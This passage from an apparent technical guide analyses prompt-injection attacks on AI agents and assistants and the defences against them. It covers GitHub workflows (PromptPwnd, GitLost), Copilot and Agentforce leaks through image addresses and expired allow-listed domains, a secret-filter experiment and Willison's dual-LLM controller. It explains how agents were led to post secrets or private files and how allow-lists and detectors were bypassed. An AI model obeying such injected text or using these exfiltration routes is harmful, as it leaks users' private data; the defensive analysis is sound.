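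The result on Llama still shows why the list should be in code, where the program checks it and a stranger's review can't add an entry.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend such checks in the application and on the network, and consider those in the application the most important. They tested neither, so the argument for them is based on how they work. If TicketOracle's tool accepted only an event name from a fixed list, and the code wrote the address, the model's output couldn't specify the administrative service. If a tool has to accept whole addresses, its developer would also need to check the destination after each redirect, because a permitted site can redirect a request to a forbidden one.

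A network allow-list would guard against mistakes in that code by letting the chatbot connect only to the event service. The common rule of blocking all private addresses would break TicketOracle, which keeps its event data at a private address, so the network would have to permit that one address and block all others. The administrative service should also require a login, since it currently accepts any request from its own machine as if an administrator had sent it.

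## GitHub automation: from pasted scripts to checked write requests

Many software projects run relay programs that can edit the project. GitHub Actions, GitHub's automation service, runs a *workflow*, a file of scripted steps, whenever something happens in a project, such as a stranger opening an issue. Some maintainers now have a model triage new issues by sorting them and suggesting what to do next. The steps that follow often have a token, or access key, that lets them change the project, so mishandling the model's reply can damage it.

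### Text pasted into a script

Suppose a workflow asks a model to summarise issue 42 in one sentence and posts the summary as a comment:

```yaml
- run: gh issue comment 42 --body "${{ steps.triage.outputs.response }}"
```

GitHub replaces the expression in double braces with the model's reply before passing the line to the shell, the program that runs typed commands. Nothing in the line the shell receives shows which characters the maintainer wrote and which the model wrote.

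This can go wrong even without an attacker. Programmers usually put names from code between backticks, and so do models. A report about a faulty table might produce this summary:

```text
The `date` column sorts wrongly.
```

A shell runs any command it finds between backticks and inserts the output, even inside double quotation marks. A comment that included `date` in backticks would therefore have today's date and time in the middle of the sentence. A stranger who could get the model to put a different command between the backticks could run it with all the access the job has. GitHub's sample script for labelling spam had the same kind of fault, because it pasted the model's reply into its own source code.

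The repair is to pass the reply as an environment variable:

```yaml
- env:
    SUMMARY: ${{ steps.triage.outputs.response }}
  run: gh issue comment 42 --body "$SUMMARY"
```

The script now contains only the variable's name. The shell parses the line before it inserts the value, and it doesn't search the value for commands. The quotation marks around `$SUMMARY` are still necessary because without them the shell would split the summary at each space, and `gh` could read some of the words as options.

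If the workflow applies a label instead of posting a comment, it should accept only labels that already exist:

```bash
case "$LABEL" in
  bug|question|documentation)
    gh issue edit 42 --add-label "$LABEL" ;;
  *)
    echo "Unknown label: leaving the issue for a maintainer" ;;
esac
```

The model then can't invent a label, as it could with GitHub's sample script. A short list like this one is safer than accepting every label in the project, because some projects use labels to start other jobs, such as software releases, and triage doesn't require those labels.

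### PromptPwnd

In December 2025 the security company Aikido disclosed PromptPwnd, a group of flaws in workflows that use models. Daelman reported in *PromptPwnd* that at least five Fortune 500 companies were affected. Their workflows gave a model untrusted text along with powerful tools or tokens, and some used the model's reply in shell commands.

Daelman's most detailed example shows why environment variables are not enough. Google used a workflow to triage issues about Gemini CLI, its coding agent for the command line. The workflow kept each issue's title and text in environment variables, so a stranger couldn't use a quotation mark to inject commands into the script. But it also put the title and text into the prompt of an agent that could run commands. The agent's environment held a key for Gemini, a Google Cloud token and a GitHub token that could edit issues and pull requests.

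Aikido's test issue reported a broken login button and included an instruction that imitated one of the project's own instruction files. The agent followed the instruction and replaced the text of the issue with two of the secrets. The instruction referred to the secrets by the names of their environment variables, so the attacker didn't need to know their values.

Google had limited the agent to four commands, for printing text and for viewing, editing and commenting on an issue. The attack needed only the editing command. This allow-list controlled which commands the agent could run, but not what text it could put in them.

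Aikido ran the test on a private copy of the project with test credentials. CyberScoop quoted Daelman's claim that this was one of the first verified cases of prompt injection compromising GitHub Actions workflows. The test shows that a workflow Google was using had the flaw, but not that anyone had exploited it.

Google fixed the workflow within four days of Aikido's report. In the other products that Daelman examined, the danger came from optional settings. Anthropic's Claude Code action and OpenAI's Codex action normally run only when the person who triggered them can write to the project, but a maintainer can let anyone trigger them. When a maintainer had done this with Claude Code, Aikido could almost always obtain a privileged GitHub token. This worked even when the workflow left the stranger's text out of the prompt, because Claude fetched it with its own tools. Codex was vulnerable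 only if the maintainer had also changed a second safety setting. GitHub's AI Inference action was exposed if the maintainer had connected the model to GitHub's tools.

Aikido recommends giving agents fewer tools, checking their output before running it, and restricting which internet addresses can use a token. The address restriction wouldn't have stopped Google's secrets from appearing on the page, but it would have made a stolen GitHub token harder to use.

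### A request file and a separate write job

On 11 June 2026, GitHub (2026) released a public preview of Agentic Workflows, which gives the agent no write access. A maintainer writes a file with a block of settings followed by a task description in ordinary English, and a compiler turns it into a standard Actions workflow.

GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026) sets out how such a workflow makes changes. Version 1.21.0, a working draft from May, divides the work between two jobs. The agent job runs the model with a token that can only read. If the model wants to comment on an issue, it calls a tool named `add_comment`, which doesn't post anything. A small server behind the tool checks the form of the request and adds it to a file as one line of JSON:

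```json
{"type": "add_comment", "item_number": 42, "body": "@dana This looks like #17. There is a workaround at https://tables.example/sort"}
```

When the agent finishes, GitHub stores the file as an artifact, a saved output of the run. The write job then downloads it. This job holds the token that can post comments and contains only ordinary code, which checks each line and calls GitHub on the agent's behalf. An attacker who takes over the agent can fill the file with hostile requests but can't post any of them directly.

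The server that writes the file runs alongside the agent, so a compromised agent might bypass the server and alter the file. The specification therefore requires the write job to repeat the server's checks on a comment's length, mentions and links.

The agent also exposes fewer secrets than the one in Google's workflow. According to GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026), a firewall restricts the agent's internet access, and a separate proxy connects it to the model so that the agent's container doesn't hold the model's key.

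If a line in the file isn't valid JSON, the write job skips it with a warning and processes the others. A maintainer whose requests depend on each other, such as a label and a comment explaining it, might prefer to hold the entire file if any line is invalid.

### One comment, seven stages

The write job puts each request through seven stages in a fixed order. A failure in any of the first six prevents the call to GitHub. The table shows how the comment to Dana moves through the stages under the default settings.

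| Stage | What happens to the comment |
|---|---|
| 1. Schema check | It passes, because the body is text, the item number is a number and there are no unknown fields |
| 2. Count limit | It passes, because the run has requested one comment and the default limit is one |
| 3. Sanitisation | The program changes `@dana` to `@ dana`, unless she is on a list of people it may notify |
| 4. Domain filtering | Nothing, because the list of permitted domains is empty |
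| 5. Repository check | It passes, because the issue is in the workflow's own repository |
| 6. References | Nothing, because the comment doesn't refer to an item the run has yet to create |
| 7. API call | The program posts the comment, with a footer linking to the run |

The schema check stops the agent from adding extra fields, but the body is free text. A comment can have up to 65,536 characters, including the footer, with at most ten mentions and fifty links. Text of that length can carry about 430,000 bits.

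If the agent requests two comments when the limit is one, the program rejects both. This prevents one run from flooding a project, but it also lets an attacker suppress a legitimate comment by getting the agent to request another. The limit applies to each run separately, so a stranger who opens a hundred issues could still cause a hundred comments. A maintainer can also remove the limit by setting it to −1.

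Sanitisation mostly means escaping text that other software could act on when it reads the comment. The program adds a space after the @ sign to prevent a notification. It puts a backslash before a command such as `/close` at the start of a comment, because another bot might obey it. It also removes invisible characters, links that use unusual protocols and HTML tags that could run code.

These rules don't apply inside code blocks. The exemption makes sense for a browser, because GitHub displays code blocks literally and changing their contents would corrupt legitimate examples. But people often copy commands from code blocks into their own terminals. If a stranger gets the agent to recommend a harmful command, the program will post it unaltered in the project's official reply.

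Domain filtering is off until the maintainer lists the permitted domains, so by default Dana's colleagues would see the link to the workaround wherever it led. If the list contained only github.com, the program would replace the address with a notice that it had removed an unauthorised link.

The draft gives conflicting rules for requests that target another repository. Its security chapter requires the program to refuse them all if the maintainer hasn't written an allow-list, but its settings chapter treats an empty list as no restriction. Both chapters always allow a workflow to write to its own repository. A cautious maintainer should write an allow-list and test that the program rejects requests to a repository that isn't on it.

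Labels get a stricter check than prose. If the agent asks to create an issue with a label that doesn't exist, the request fails, and the maintainer can restrict the agent to a shorter list of labels. This gives the same protection as the `case` statement in the repaired script, but maintainers no longer have to write the check by hand.

### A model as the last reviewer

A detection job runs between the agent and the write job. By default, according to GitHub's *Threat Detection*, it gives the agent's requests to a model, which returns true or false for each of three threats: a prompt injection, a leaked secret and a malicious code change. A single "true" blocks every write, and so does a failure of the detection job.

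The detection job has no write access, so an attacker who fools its model only gets requests passed to the write job, which still has to check them. The model can be wrong. It normally comes from the same provider as the agent's model, so the two may share weaknesses, and it reads text that the attacker may have influenced. A maintainer can choose a different model, add conventional scanners or switch detection off.

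GitHub's documentation includes sample code for adding Llama Guard, a safety classifier from Meta that answers "safe" or "unsafe". The sample converts the answer to lower case and lets the workflow continue if it contains the word "safe". Because "unsafe" contains "safe", the check approves everything that Llama Guard rejects, the same mistake as in the first moderation example. Checking that the answer is exactly "safe" would fix it.

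The specification also describes a warn mode. If the detector reports a threat in this mode, the write job discards requests to add labels but still posts comments, with a prominent caution. The caution can help when a comment contains a suspicious link, but it doesn't protect private data, because anyone who can read the caution can read the data too.

### GitLost

In July 2026 the security company Noma showed that a comment could pass all these checks and still leak a private file. Levi's *GitLost* described a workflow that ran whenever someone assigned an issue to a person. The workflow read the issue's title and text and posted a comment in reply. It could also read other repositories in the same organisation, including private ones.

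Levi opened an issue in a public repository, posing as a sales executive who had just met a customer. He asked, among other things, about a private repository's README file (its introductory document). An automated process assigned the issue, and the assignment started the workflow. The agent fetched the README files of both the public and the private repository and posted them in a public comment.

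The product's guardrails were supposed to prevent this, but Levi tried different wordings until one got through. That wording presented the request as an addition to the existing task. The attacker needed no password, programming skill or membership of the organisation.

The comment contained nothing that the seven stages were designed to catch. It was text in the correct field, and the agent posted only one comment. A README contains ordinary prose and formatting, so sanitisation had little to remove. Even a strict domain filter wouldn't have helped, because the private information was in the comment itself and not in a link. The repository check controls where the agent writes, and the agent wrote to the public repository where the workflow was running. It had only read from the private one. Finally, the write job had permission to post comments.

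The specification's only measure against leaks concerns credentials. GitHub masks registered secrets, and scanners and, by default, the detection model look for text that resembles a key or password, which a README usually doesn't contain. GitHub's *Security Architecture* adds that the detection model receives the agent's output and the workflow's prompt but has no access to the live repositories, so it can't check whether a paragraph came from a private file.

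GitHub also neutralises mentions, HTML tags and links to untrusted sites in an issue before the agent reads it. These changes don't affect a request written in plain English, so GitHub overstates the protection when it marks the result as safe for AI consumption in a diagram.

None of the checks concerned confidentiality, because the request file lacks the information they would need. Each line gives the text of a comment and the issue it belongs to, but not where the text came from. A program can't decide whether a paragraph is confidential without knowing who was allowed to read the original and who will be able to read the copy. GitHub uses "provenance" to mean the footer, which identifies the workflow that posted the comment. CaMeL, a design for AI agents, instead attaches a provenance label to each value.

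Blocking the comment might not have kept the README private either. Anyone signed in to GitHub can normally download a public repository's artifacts, including the request file, so the text could have been available before the write job started. It would have been safer not to give the agent the README.

### Whose fault it was

Noma presented GitLost as a critical vulnerability in GitHub's product. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* puts more of the blame on a workflow with more access than it needed and a guardrail that an attacker could get the model to ignore.

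Somebody chose to give the agent access to the other repositories, because the token that GitHub Actions supplies by default covers only the workflow's own repository. A maintainer who had kept the default token wouldn't have been exposed to this attack. Vijendra Malhotra, a technology executive quoted in InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026), advises treating everything in a private repository that an agent can read as "one well-crafted issue away from public".

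In March, GitHub's *Under the hood* post had already warned of this route, in which a compromised agent hides secrets in public issues, pull requests and comments. The compiler already rejects some dangerous settings, and it could also warn a maintainer who combines a trigger open to strangers, access to private repositories and public replies. Any two of those are much less dangerous than all three. Relying on the model's guardrail was a poor substitute for such a check, because Levi could keep rewording the request until the model complied.

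Noma told GitHub about the problem before publishing and suggested adding a note to the documentation to warn teams about sharing keys between repositories. According to The Next Web's *‘GitLost’*, GitHub had not added the note when the story came out and didn't respond to questions from The Register, a technology news site.

### Choosing what the agent can read

GitHub had already released a feature that could have prevented the attack if the maintainer had configured it. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group GitHub Next, describes a filter that removes untrusted posts before the agent sees them. It came out on 26 May 2026, about six weeks before Levi's post. The filter gives each item one of five levels.

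| Level | What it covers |
|---|---|
| Merged | Merged pull requests and code on the project's main branch |
| Approved | Posts by owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private repositories |
| Unapproved | Posts by other contributors, including first-time contributors |
| None | Posts by anonymous users and new users with no history |
| Blocked | Posts by users the maintainer has blocked |

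The maintainer sets a minimum level and lists the repositories the agent may read:

```yaml
tools:
  github:
    repos: "public"
    min-integrity: approved
```

Either setting would probably have stopped GitLost. With `min-integrity: approved`, the agent wouldn't have seen an outsider's issue unless a maintainer had endorsed it. With `repos: "public"`, it could have read and obeyed the issue but couldn't have fetched the private file. The repository setting is the better safeguard here because it doesn't depend on working out whom to trust.

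The minimum level is awkward for triage, which exists to read what outsiders send. GitHub Next suggests setting it to "unapproved" for such workflows, which excludes only the least-known accounts. An attacker could get past that with an account that has some history.

Maintainers can also raise the level of a single post. They can choose a label that marks a post as approved, or have the filter treat a maintainer's thumbs-up as approval. The thumbs-up is convenient, but a maintainer might give one to thank someone for a detailed report without meaning to let an agent act on it. A team that uses this option should also check whether the author can edit the post after approval. The triage agent should never be able to apply the approval label.

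The filter can't prevent leaks, as GitHub Next acknowledges, because it controls which text can influence the agent and not where the agent's knowledge goes. The private README would have counted as trustworthy. The underlying design does include a rule for secrecy. Each agent and each destination has a set of tags for the private repositories it may receive data from, and an agent may write to a destination only if

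*S*(agent) ⊆ *S*(destination),

which means that every tag on the agent must also be on the destination. In Levi's test, the agent could read a private repository called `testlocal`, so its set would be {`testlocal`}. A public issue has an empty set. Since {`testlocal`} is not a subset of the empty set, the rule would have refused the comment.

When GitHub Next described the filter, the system recorded these tags but did not enforce the rule. Enforcing it would prevent an agent that could read `testlocal` from posting any public comment, even one that only thanked the reporter.

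Hostile text can also reach a trusted agent through its memory. Agentic Workflows can save notes in a cache for later runs, so a stranger's issue might lead one run to save a false note that a more trusted run then relies on. Under the Safe Outputs specification, each trust level has a separate cache. A run can use notes from more trusted runs, but not from less trusted ones.

The draft contains an exception that weakens this separation. If a run finds no suitable cache, it may load any cache whose name begins with `memory-`, a rule that GitHub kept so that older caches would still work. The names of all the new caches also begin with `memory-`, so a trusted run could load one that an untrusted run had saved. The protection would then depend on the Git branches, or parallel versions of the files, which also keep the notes for each level separate.

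### Custom jobs and enclaves

GitHub made Agentic Workflows generally available on its Free, Team and Enterprise plans on 28 October 2026 (Rojas, 2026, *GitHub Agentic Workflows open source tool reaches general availability*). According to InfoQ's *GitHub Makes Agentic Workflows Generally Available with Isolation and Budget Controls* (2026), the tool's protections don't cover workflows in which the maintainer grants write permission directly or adds custom jobs.

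A custom job can therefore bring back the original mistake. If a maintainer adds a step that pastes the agent's summary into a shell command to update a release page, the shell will run any text between backticks in the summary. This happens even though the agent still has a read-only token and its comments still go through seven stages. The maintainer has to treat the summary as untrusted text again and pass it as an environment variable. The custom job should also have its own narrow token and limits on what it can change.

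In November, GitHub introduced *enclaves* for workflows that need several repositories. GitHub Next's *Research & ideas* describes them as a way to let agents work on different repositories while limiting the information they exchange. In a workflow like Levi's, one agent could read the private repository while another handled the public issue. The agent handling the issue would have no access to the README, so an attacker who posted a hostile issue would have to extract the text through the messages between the two agents.

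The protection depends on how much those messages can carry. If the private agent can reply with a paragraph, it could send the opening of the README. It would reveal far less if the public agent could ask only whether a bug is already known and the private agent could answer only yes or no. The maintainer would still need to limit the number of questions, because a stranger can open more than one issue.

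## Chat assistants: filtering links, images and secrets out of replies

GitLost leaked a private file by posting it in public. A company's chat assistant can also leak private text, even though it shows its reply only to the employee who asked the question. The software that displays the reply can send part of it to an outsider while drawing the screen.

### How displaying a reply can leak it

Chat models usually format their replies in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and pictures. The chat interface is a relay program that converts this notation into HTML for the browser. Suppose the museum's assistant answers a visitor with a floor plan:

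```text
![Floor plan](https://museum.example/plan.png?room=4)
```

The interface turns this line into an image tag, and the browser requests the picture from museum.example. The request contains everything after the site's name, so whoever runs the museum's server can see that someone is looking at room 4.

An attacker can steal private data when a model reads it together with untrusted text. An instruction injected into the text gets the model to write an image address that points to the attacker's server and contains the private data. As Microsoft (2025) explains, the browser sends the data when it tries to load the image, whereas a link leaks the data only if the user clicks it. An address with 1,000 characters, each chosen from 64, can carry 6,000 bits, enough for more than 100 card numbers of 16 digits each.

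Escaping the whole reply for HTML would prevent this, but the user would see raw notation instead of tables and links. The interface has to convert some of the model's text into HTML elements, so it needs rules about which elements to allow.

### EchoLeak

In June 2025 the company Aim Security disclosed EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions using their emails, files and chats. The attacker only had to send an employee an email. If the employee later asked Copilot about a subject the email seemed to cover, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal material. Instructions in the email then led the model to put sensitive information into an image address.

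Microsoft had several checks that should have stopped this. The first was a trained classifier, and the others were fixed rules. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how each one failed.

| Check | Purpose | Why it failed |
|---|---|---|
| Injection classifier | Keep hostile emails from the model | The email read like a request to its human recipient |
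| Link filter | Remove outside links from replies | It missed some of the ways to write a link in Markdown |
| Image filter | Remove outside images from replies | It had the same gap |
| Browser allow-list | Load images only from approved domains | An approved Microsoft Teams service would fetch any address it was given |

The link and image filters looked for particular patterns of characters, while the interface accepted every pattern that Markdown allows. A safer program would parse the reply with the same parser as the interface and then check the result. In outline:

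```python
for image in parse_markdown(reply).images():
    if image.address not in ALLOWED_IMAGES:
        image.replace_with(image.description)
```

The parser produces the same kind of object however the model writes an image, so the check can't miss an image because it is written unusually. The program should treat links the same way, and display any HTML in the reply as plain text, since HTML has its own image tags.

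The browser's allow-list is part of a *content security policy*, the rules a website sends to tell the browser what it may load. The list Ravia reproduces has 29 different entries, 11 of which are wildcards that cover every subdomain of a site. The browser enforced the list correctly, but the Teams service, which fetches web content for Microsoft's own software, then passed the request on to the attacker's server. The browser checks only the first destination, so any approved service that fetches other addresses can pass requests on to any server on the internet.

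Aim reported the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had used the flaw against customers. According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Copilot now strips embedded images and the overlooked style of link from incoming outside content, and Microsoft reportedly added options to exclude outside messages from some of Copilot's work.

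The first change is weak on its own because, as in the DeepSeek demonstration, the model can write markup that its input didn't contain. The second is stronger, since an email can't cause the model to leak internal files if the model never reads the two together, but it makes Copilot less useful to an employee whose question depends on a client's email. Microsoft says it also uses fixed rules to block leaks through Markdown images and certain untrusted links in its products' output.

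### Later leaks from Copilot

These fixes did not end the problem. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (June 2026) described an attack on Copilot's enterprise search that began when an employee clicked a link to Microsoft's own site. The link contained a search query, which Copilot treated as instructions. Microsoft's software neutralised HTML in the reply only after the reply was complete. Copilot displays its replies as the model writes them, so the browser had already requested an image in the reply by then.

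The allow-list failed much as it had in EchoLeak. This time the approved service was Bing's image search, which fetched the attacker's address to analyse the picture. Bing was on the list that Aim had published a year earlier.

A program can avoid the timing problem by checking the complete reply before showing any of it, but the user then sees an empty screen for several seconds. It could instead show plain text while the model is writing and add the formatting after the check. The user would briefly see raw formatting symbols, but the browser couldn't load an image before the check because the page would contain no image tag.

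On 3 December 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot that needed no click. The former Aim research team, now part of Cato Networks, found them. The attacks sent data out through an image address, a link in a saved file, or code that Copilot ran (AIAIAI.FYI, *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot*, 2026). The last route worked even though Microsoft's documentation said the code's sandbox blocked outgoing traffic. Microsoft fixed all three between 17 September and 15 November, and the researchers know of no case in which they were used against real targets.

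According to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026), the image route went through Bing again, though possibly through a different feature. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes the researchers as saying that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. The researchers sell protection against such attacks, but the repeated use of Bing supports their assessment. Closing one forwarding service at a time leaves the others on the list.

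### ForcedLeak and the expired domain

An allow-list can also fail because a domain on it changes hands. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces a report by Noma, the company that later found GitLost, about Salesforce's Agentforce, which lets AI agents work with a company's customer records. Noma put instructions in the description field of a public web form for prospective customers. The field accepted 42,000 characters. When an employee later asked the agent to deal with the enquiry, the agent also followed Noma's instructions. It collected the email addresses of other prospective customers and put them into an image address.

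Salesforce's content security policy allowed images only from approved domains. One of these, my-salesforce-cms.com, had expired, and Noma bought it for $5. The browser then sent the data to Noma's server because the domain was still approved.

In EchoLeak, Microsoft owned the approved domain but ran a service there that would forward requests. In ForcedLeak, Salesforce no longer owned the approved domain. A test of the browser's rule would have passed in both cases, because the browser enforced its list of approved domains.

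The list may have had other weak entries besides the expired domain. It included wildcards for Amazon's cloud and for Cloudinary, an image-hosting company, both of which rent space to outsiders. PromptArmor, a security company, advises against wildcard entries for any site that hosts content from its users.

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025 and published its findings on 25 September. The Hacker News (2025) reports that Salesforce recovered the domain and began enforcing a second allow-list on the addresses its agents generate or call. This second check covers links as well as images, but it can also fail if a listed domain expires and an attacker buys it.

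A company can use ordinary code to help keep its allow-list up to date. For its own domains, a nightly job can compare the list with the company's domain registrar account and remove any domain that is missing or about to expire. For other companies' domains, each entry can have an end date, after which the program refuses the domain until someone checks it again. Some images won't load when a reviewer is late, but that is better than sending customer data to whoever bought an expired domain.

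A list of web addresses also leaves other routes open, since an agent that can send email can leak data without an image. In April 2026 the company Capsule Security disclosed leaks from Agentforce and from Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents. Both attacks started from public forms, according to OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce AI* (2026). Claw Times reported that Microsoft's January patch for Copilot Studio had not fully prevented the leak, and that Salesforce began requiring a person to confirm its agents' email actions by default.

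### A filter with a perfect record

A program can search each reply for the secret itself instead of restricting addresses. Deep, Emmons and colleagues tested this in April 2026 in *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*. They put three invented secrets (an authentication token, a database ID and an escalation code) in a chatbot's system prompt, which holds the operator's standing instructions to the model. The attacker, a program also built on a language model, chatted with the bot and tried to extract the secrets.

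The attacker sent ten messages in each round. Code scored the replies, adding 0.30 for each secret, 0.10 for the bot's name and 0.05 for each run of seven or more words copied from the system prompt. The attacker then rewrote its five best messages, looked for patterns in the bot's refusals and tried new approaches from a library of more than 40. Both sides used Gemini 2.5 Pro with its safety filters off.

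The team compared nine configurations. The table shows the round in which each one broke. A configuration counted as broken once a reply scored at least 0.9, the score for revealing all three secrets.

| Defence | Round in which it broke |
|---|---|
| None | 9 or earlier |
| Screening incoming messages | 39 |
| Rules against revealing secrets | 49 |
| Tags marking the user's message as data | 84 |
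| Ranking the operator's instructions above the user's | 247 |
| Security rules at both ends of the prompt | 277 |
| All of the above defences together | Did not break in 500 |
| Output filter alone | Did not break in 500 |
| All defences, including the output filter | Did not break in 500 |

Short tests were misleading. The defence with rules at both ends of the prompt looked nearly perfect in its first 25 rounds, with a worst score of 0.05, but that had risen to 0.95 by round 277.

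The output filter was ordinary code that blocked any reply containing text from the system prompt. The team ran it three times on its own and three times with the other defences, for 500 rounds per run, and no reply scored above zero. They report 15,000 attacks in total, but six runs of 5,000 attacks make 30,000, so 15,000 may be the total for each configuration.

The combination without an output filter never revealed a secret in a form that the scoring code could detect. In 5,000 attacks, 23 replies leaked something, but the worst score was 0.10, and revealing a single secret would have scored 0.30. Deep and colleagues, most of whom work for a company that sells AI security testing, conclude that every defence relying on the model eventually broke, which is too strong for this combination. However, it was run only once, and nothing in its design guarantees the same result in another run.

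### What the perfect record depends on

The experiment shows that the filter's code worked reliably, but it couldn't show that no information about the secrets got out, because the scoring code searched for leaks in much the same way as the filter did. The filter blocked replies that contained the secrets, and the scoring code counted a secret only if it appeared in the reply character for character, ignoring capitalization. A reply that got past the filter therefore had almost no chance of being counted as a leak.

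Deep and colleagues acknowledge that a secret could evade both checks if the model encoded it, paraphrased it or spelled it out. Re-encoded secrets have passed scanners in other systems. If a secret had leaked this way in the experiment, the scoring code would have given the reply zero, and the attacker would have had no reason to develop the method further. Each attack was also a single message, so the experiment did not test whether a secret could leak in pieces over a longer conversation.

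A programmer can make the filter recognise more forms by ignoring punctuation and spaces:

```python
import re

def squeeze(text):
    return re.sub(r"[^a-z0-9]", "", text.lower())

if any(squeeze(secret) in squeeze(reply) for secret in SECRETS):
    reply = "The assistant can't show this reply."
```

This would catch a token that the model had split with hyphens. It would still miss a token written out in words, and it would create false alarms when a secret is short. If the museum's door code were 1030, the filter would block the sentence "The tour starts at 10:30."

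Blocking fragments of a secret creates another way for it to leak. An attacker who can get the bot to repeat a guess learns from the block that the guess was right. If a filter blocks any four consecutive digits of a sixteen-digit number, the attacker has only 10,000 possible fragments to try, and the overlaps between the correct ones would usually reveal their order. The program should match long strings instead and suspend a conversation after a few blocks.

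The filter also needs a list of secrets. A developer can easily list three tokens, but nobody could list every confidential sentence in an employee's mailbox, so this filter could not have stopped EchoLeak. It would work best for passwords and access keys, which are also the easiest secrets to keep out of the prompt.

### What each restriction costs

An assistant's developer can restrict what the interface displays, where it may send requests, or what the model knows.

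| Restriction | Cost to users | What can still leak |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text only | No clickable links, formatted tables or pictures | Addresses that the user or another program opens |
| No outside images | No maps, charts or photos from other sites | Links that the user clicks |
| Exact addresses only | New links and pictures fail until someone lists them | The choice of address, to anyone who can see the requests |
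| No secret in the prompt | The assistant can't discuss the secret | Any other private data the model reads |

**Plain text** prevents the chat interface from requesting any address the model writes, but users have to copy addresses by hand and read tables as rows of symbols. The protection ends when the text leaves that interface. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* points out that a link preview, a terminal or a ticketing system may still fetch an address automatically. If an employee pastes the reply into a team chat that shows previews, the team chat may send the request that the assistant's interface avoided.

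**Blocking outside images** inconveniences users much less, since most office questions can be answered without a picture from another website. According to Checkmarx, Google does this in Gemini, so EchoLeak's image route doesn't work there. The interface can still draw charts itself from numbers in the reply. Links remain a risk, but the interface can show the full address before opening one, giving users some chance of noticing a long string of private data in it.

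With **an allow-list of exact addresses**, the program keeps only approved pictures and links. It must compare the whole address, including anything after a question mark. This would have stopped the model from using Teams or Bing to forward data, because adding the attacker's address and the data would have changed the approved address. If an approved domain expired, its new owner would receive only requests for fixed addresses, but could still replace the picture and count how often people loaded it. If the list has sixteen addresses, each address the model chooses can carry at most 4 bits of data.

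Lists in real products are usually broader, because exact addresses are tedious to maintain. Salesforce made its allow-list mandatory from 8 September 2025, and TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* warned that agents could stop working properly if administrators didn't add every outside domain the agents needed. According to Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, the assistant removes addresses by default until an administrator adds the source. The example entry covers all of docs.google.com, where anyone can create a document. This is convenient for staff who need hundreds of documents, but it loses most of the protection of an exact list.

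**Keeping a secret from the model** is the only one of these restrictions that also works against encoding and paraphrase. An access key can be withheld without any loss to users. If the museum's assistant needs to look up a booking, it can call a function that holds the key and returns only the booking. As with the shop chatbot's order numbers, the function must also check whose booking it is.

Protecting private documents limits an assistant's usefulness more. Microsoft lets companies label sensitive files so that Copilot can't summarise them, so employees have to read those files themselves. PromptArmor recommends a Salesforce setting that replaces sensitive values with placeholders before the model sees them. This prevents an agent from revealing a customer's phone number, but also from noticing that the number is missing a digit.

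No company can keep all private data from an assistant whose job is to search its files. Reddy and Gujral suggest that such an assistant answer from internal sources by default and include outside messages only when the user asks for them. This default would have kept the EchoLeak email out of the prompt when an employee asked an ordinary question about an internal project. But if the employee asks the assistant to compare a client's email with a confidential contract, the prompt will contain both, so the rules on links and images are still needed.

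## Willison's controller: placeholders in place of untrusted text

In April 2023, Willison reasoned that a model can't obey a hostile email it has never read, much as a chat assistant can't leak a key it has never seen. But people want assistants to deal with their email, so his design puts an ordinary program, the *controller*, between two language models.

The *privileged model* receives the user's request and can call tools, for example to send an email. The *quarantined model* reads untrusted text and has no tools. The design assumes an attacker could take over the quarantined model at any moment. The controller calls both models, runs the tools and displays the results. The controller must never pass the quarantined model's free text to the privileged model.

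The usual alternative was to ask the user to approve every action. Willison expected that to fail, because people would soon click "OK" without reading.

### Who sees the email

Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The controller passes the request to the privileged model, which outputs an instruction to fetch the email and name it `$VAR1`. The controller fetches the email and stores it under that name. The privileged model then outputs a prompt to summarize `$VAR1`. The controller replaces the name with the email's text and sends the prompt to the quarantined model.

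When the summary comes back, the controller stores it as `$VAR2` and sends the privileged model only a notice that the summary is ready. The privileged model writes a reply containing the name `$VAR2`, and the controller replaces that name with the summary before showing the reply to the user.

| Who | The email, `$VAR1` | The summary, `$VAR2` |
|---|---|---|
| Privileged model | Name only | Name only |
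| Quarantined model | Full text | Full text, which it writes |
| Controller | Full text | Full text |
| User | Not shown | Full text |

If the email contains an instruction to delete the mailbox, the quarantined model can't carry it out because it has no tool for deleting anything. It may write a deletion command in the summary, but the controller will store that command as text. In Dongol's formal model of this design, an injection can corrupt an answer but can't add a tool call.

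### What the privileged model may read

Willison allows one exception. If the quarantined model sorts text into fixed categories, the controller can check that its output is exactly one of them and pass it to the privileged model. The privileged model could then forward an email categorized as a complaint to the right person, though the email's author may still be able to choose the category.

A placeholder name must stand in for all other output, even after several models have processed it in turn, because Willison warns that one model can pass a hostile instruction on to the next.

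Some later designs use the name "dual LLM" but break this rule. *ORBIT* (2026), a framework for testing the safety of AI agents, includes a dual-LLM defence in which the privileged model reads the quarantined model's summary. The quarantined model is told to describe any instruction in neutral language instead of repeating it, but an attacker may be able to override that. Test results for this defence don't apply to Willison's. Google says the dual-LLM pattern partly inspired a safety check in its Chrome browser, but the model that plans Chrome's actions reads web content directly.

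### Replacing names safely

A mistake in replacing placeholder names with text can leak private data, even though this looks like the controller's easiest job. In an invented example, a museum employee asks the assistant to open a private email from a lender and to post a public reply to a visitor's comment. `$VAR1` holds the email, and `$VAR2` holds a summary of the comment. The visitor has gotten the characters "$VAR1" into that summary.

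```python
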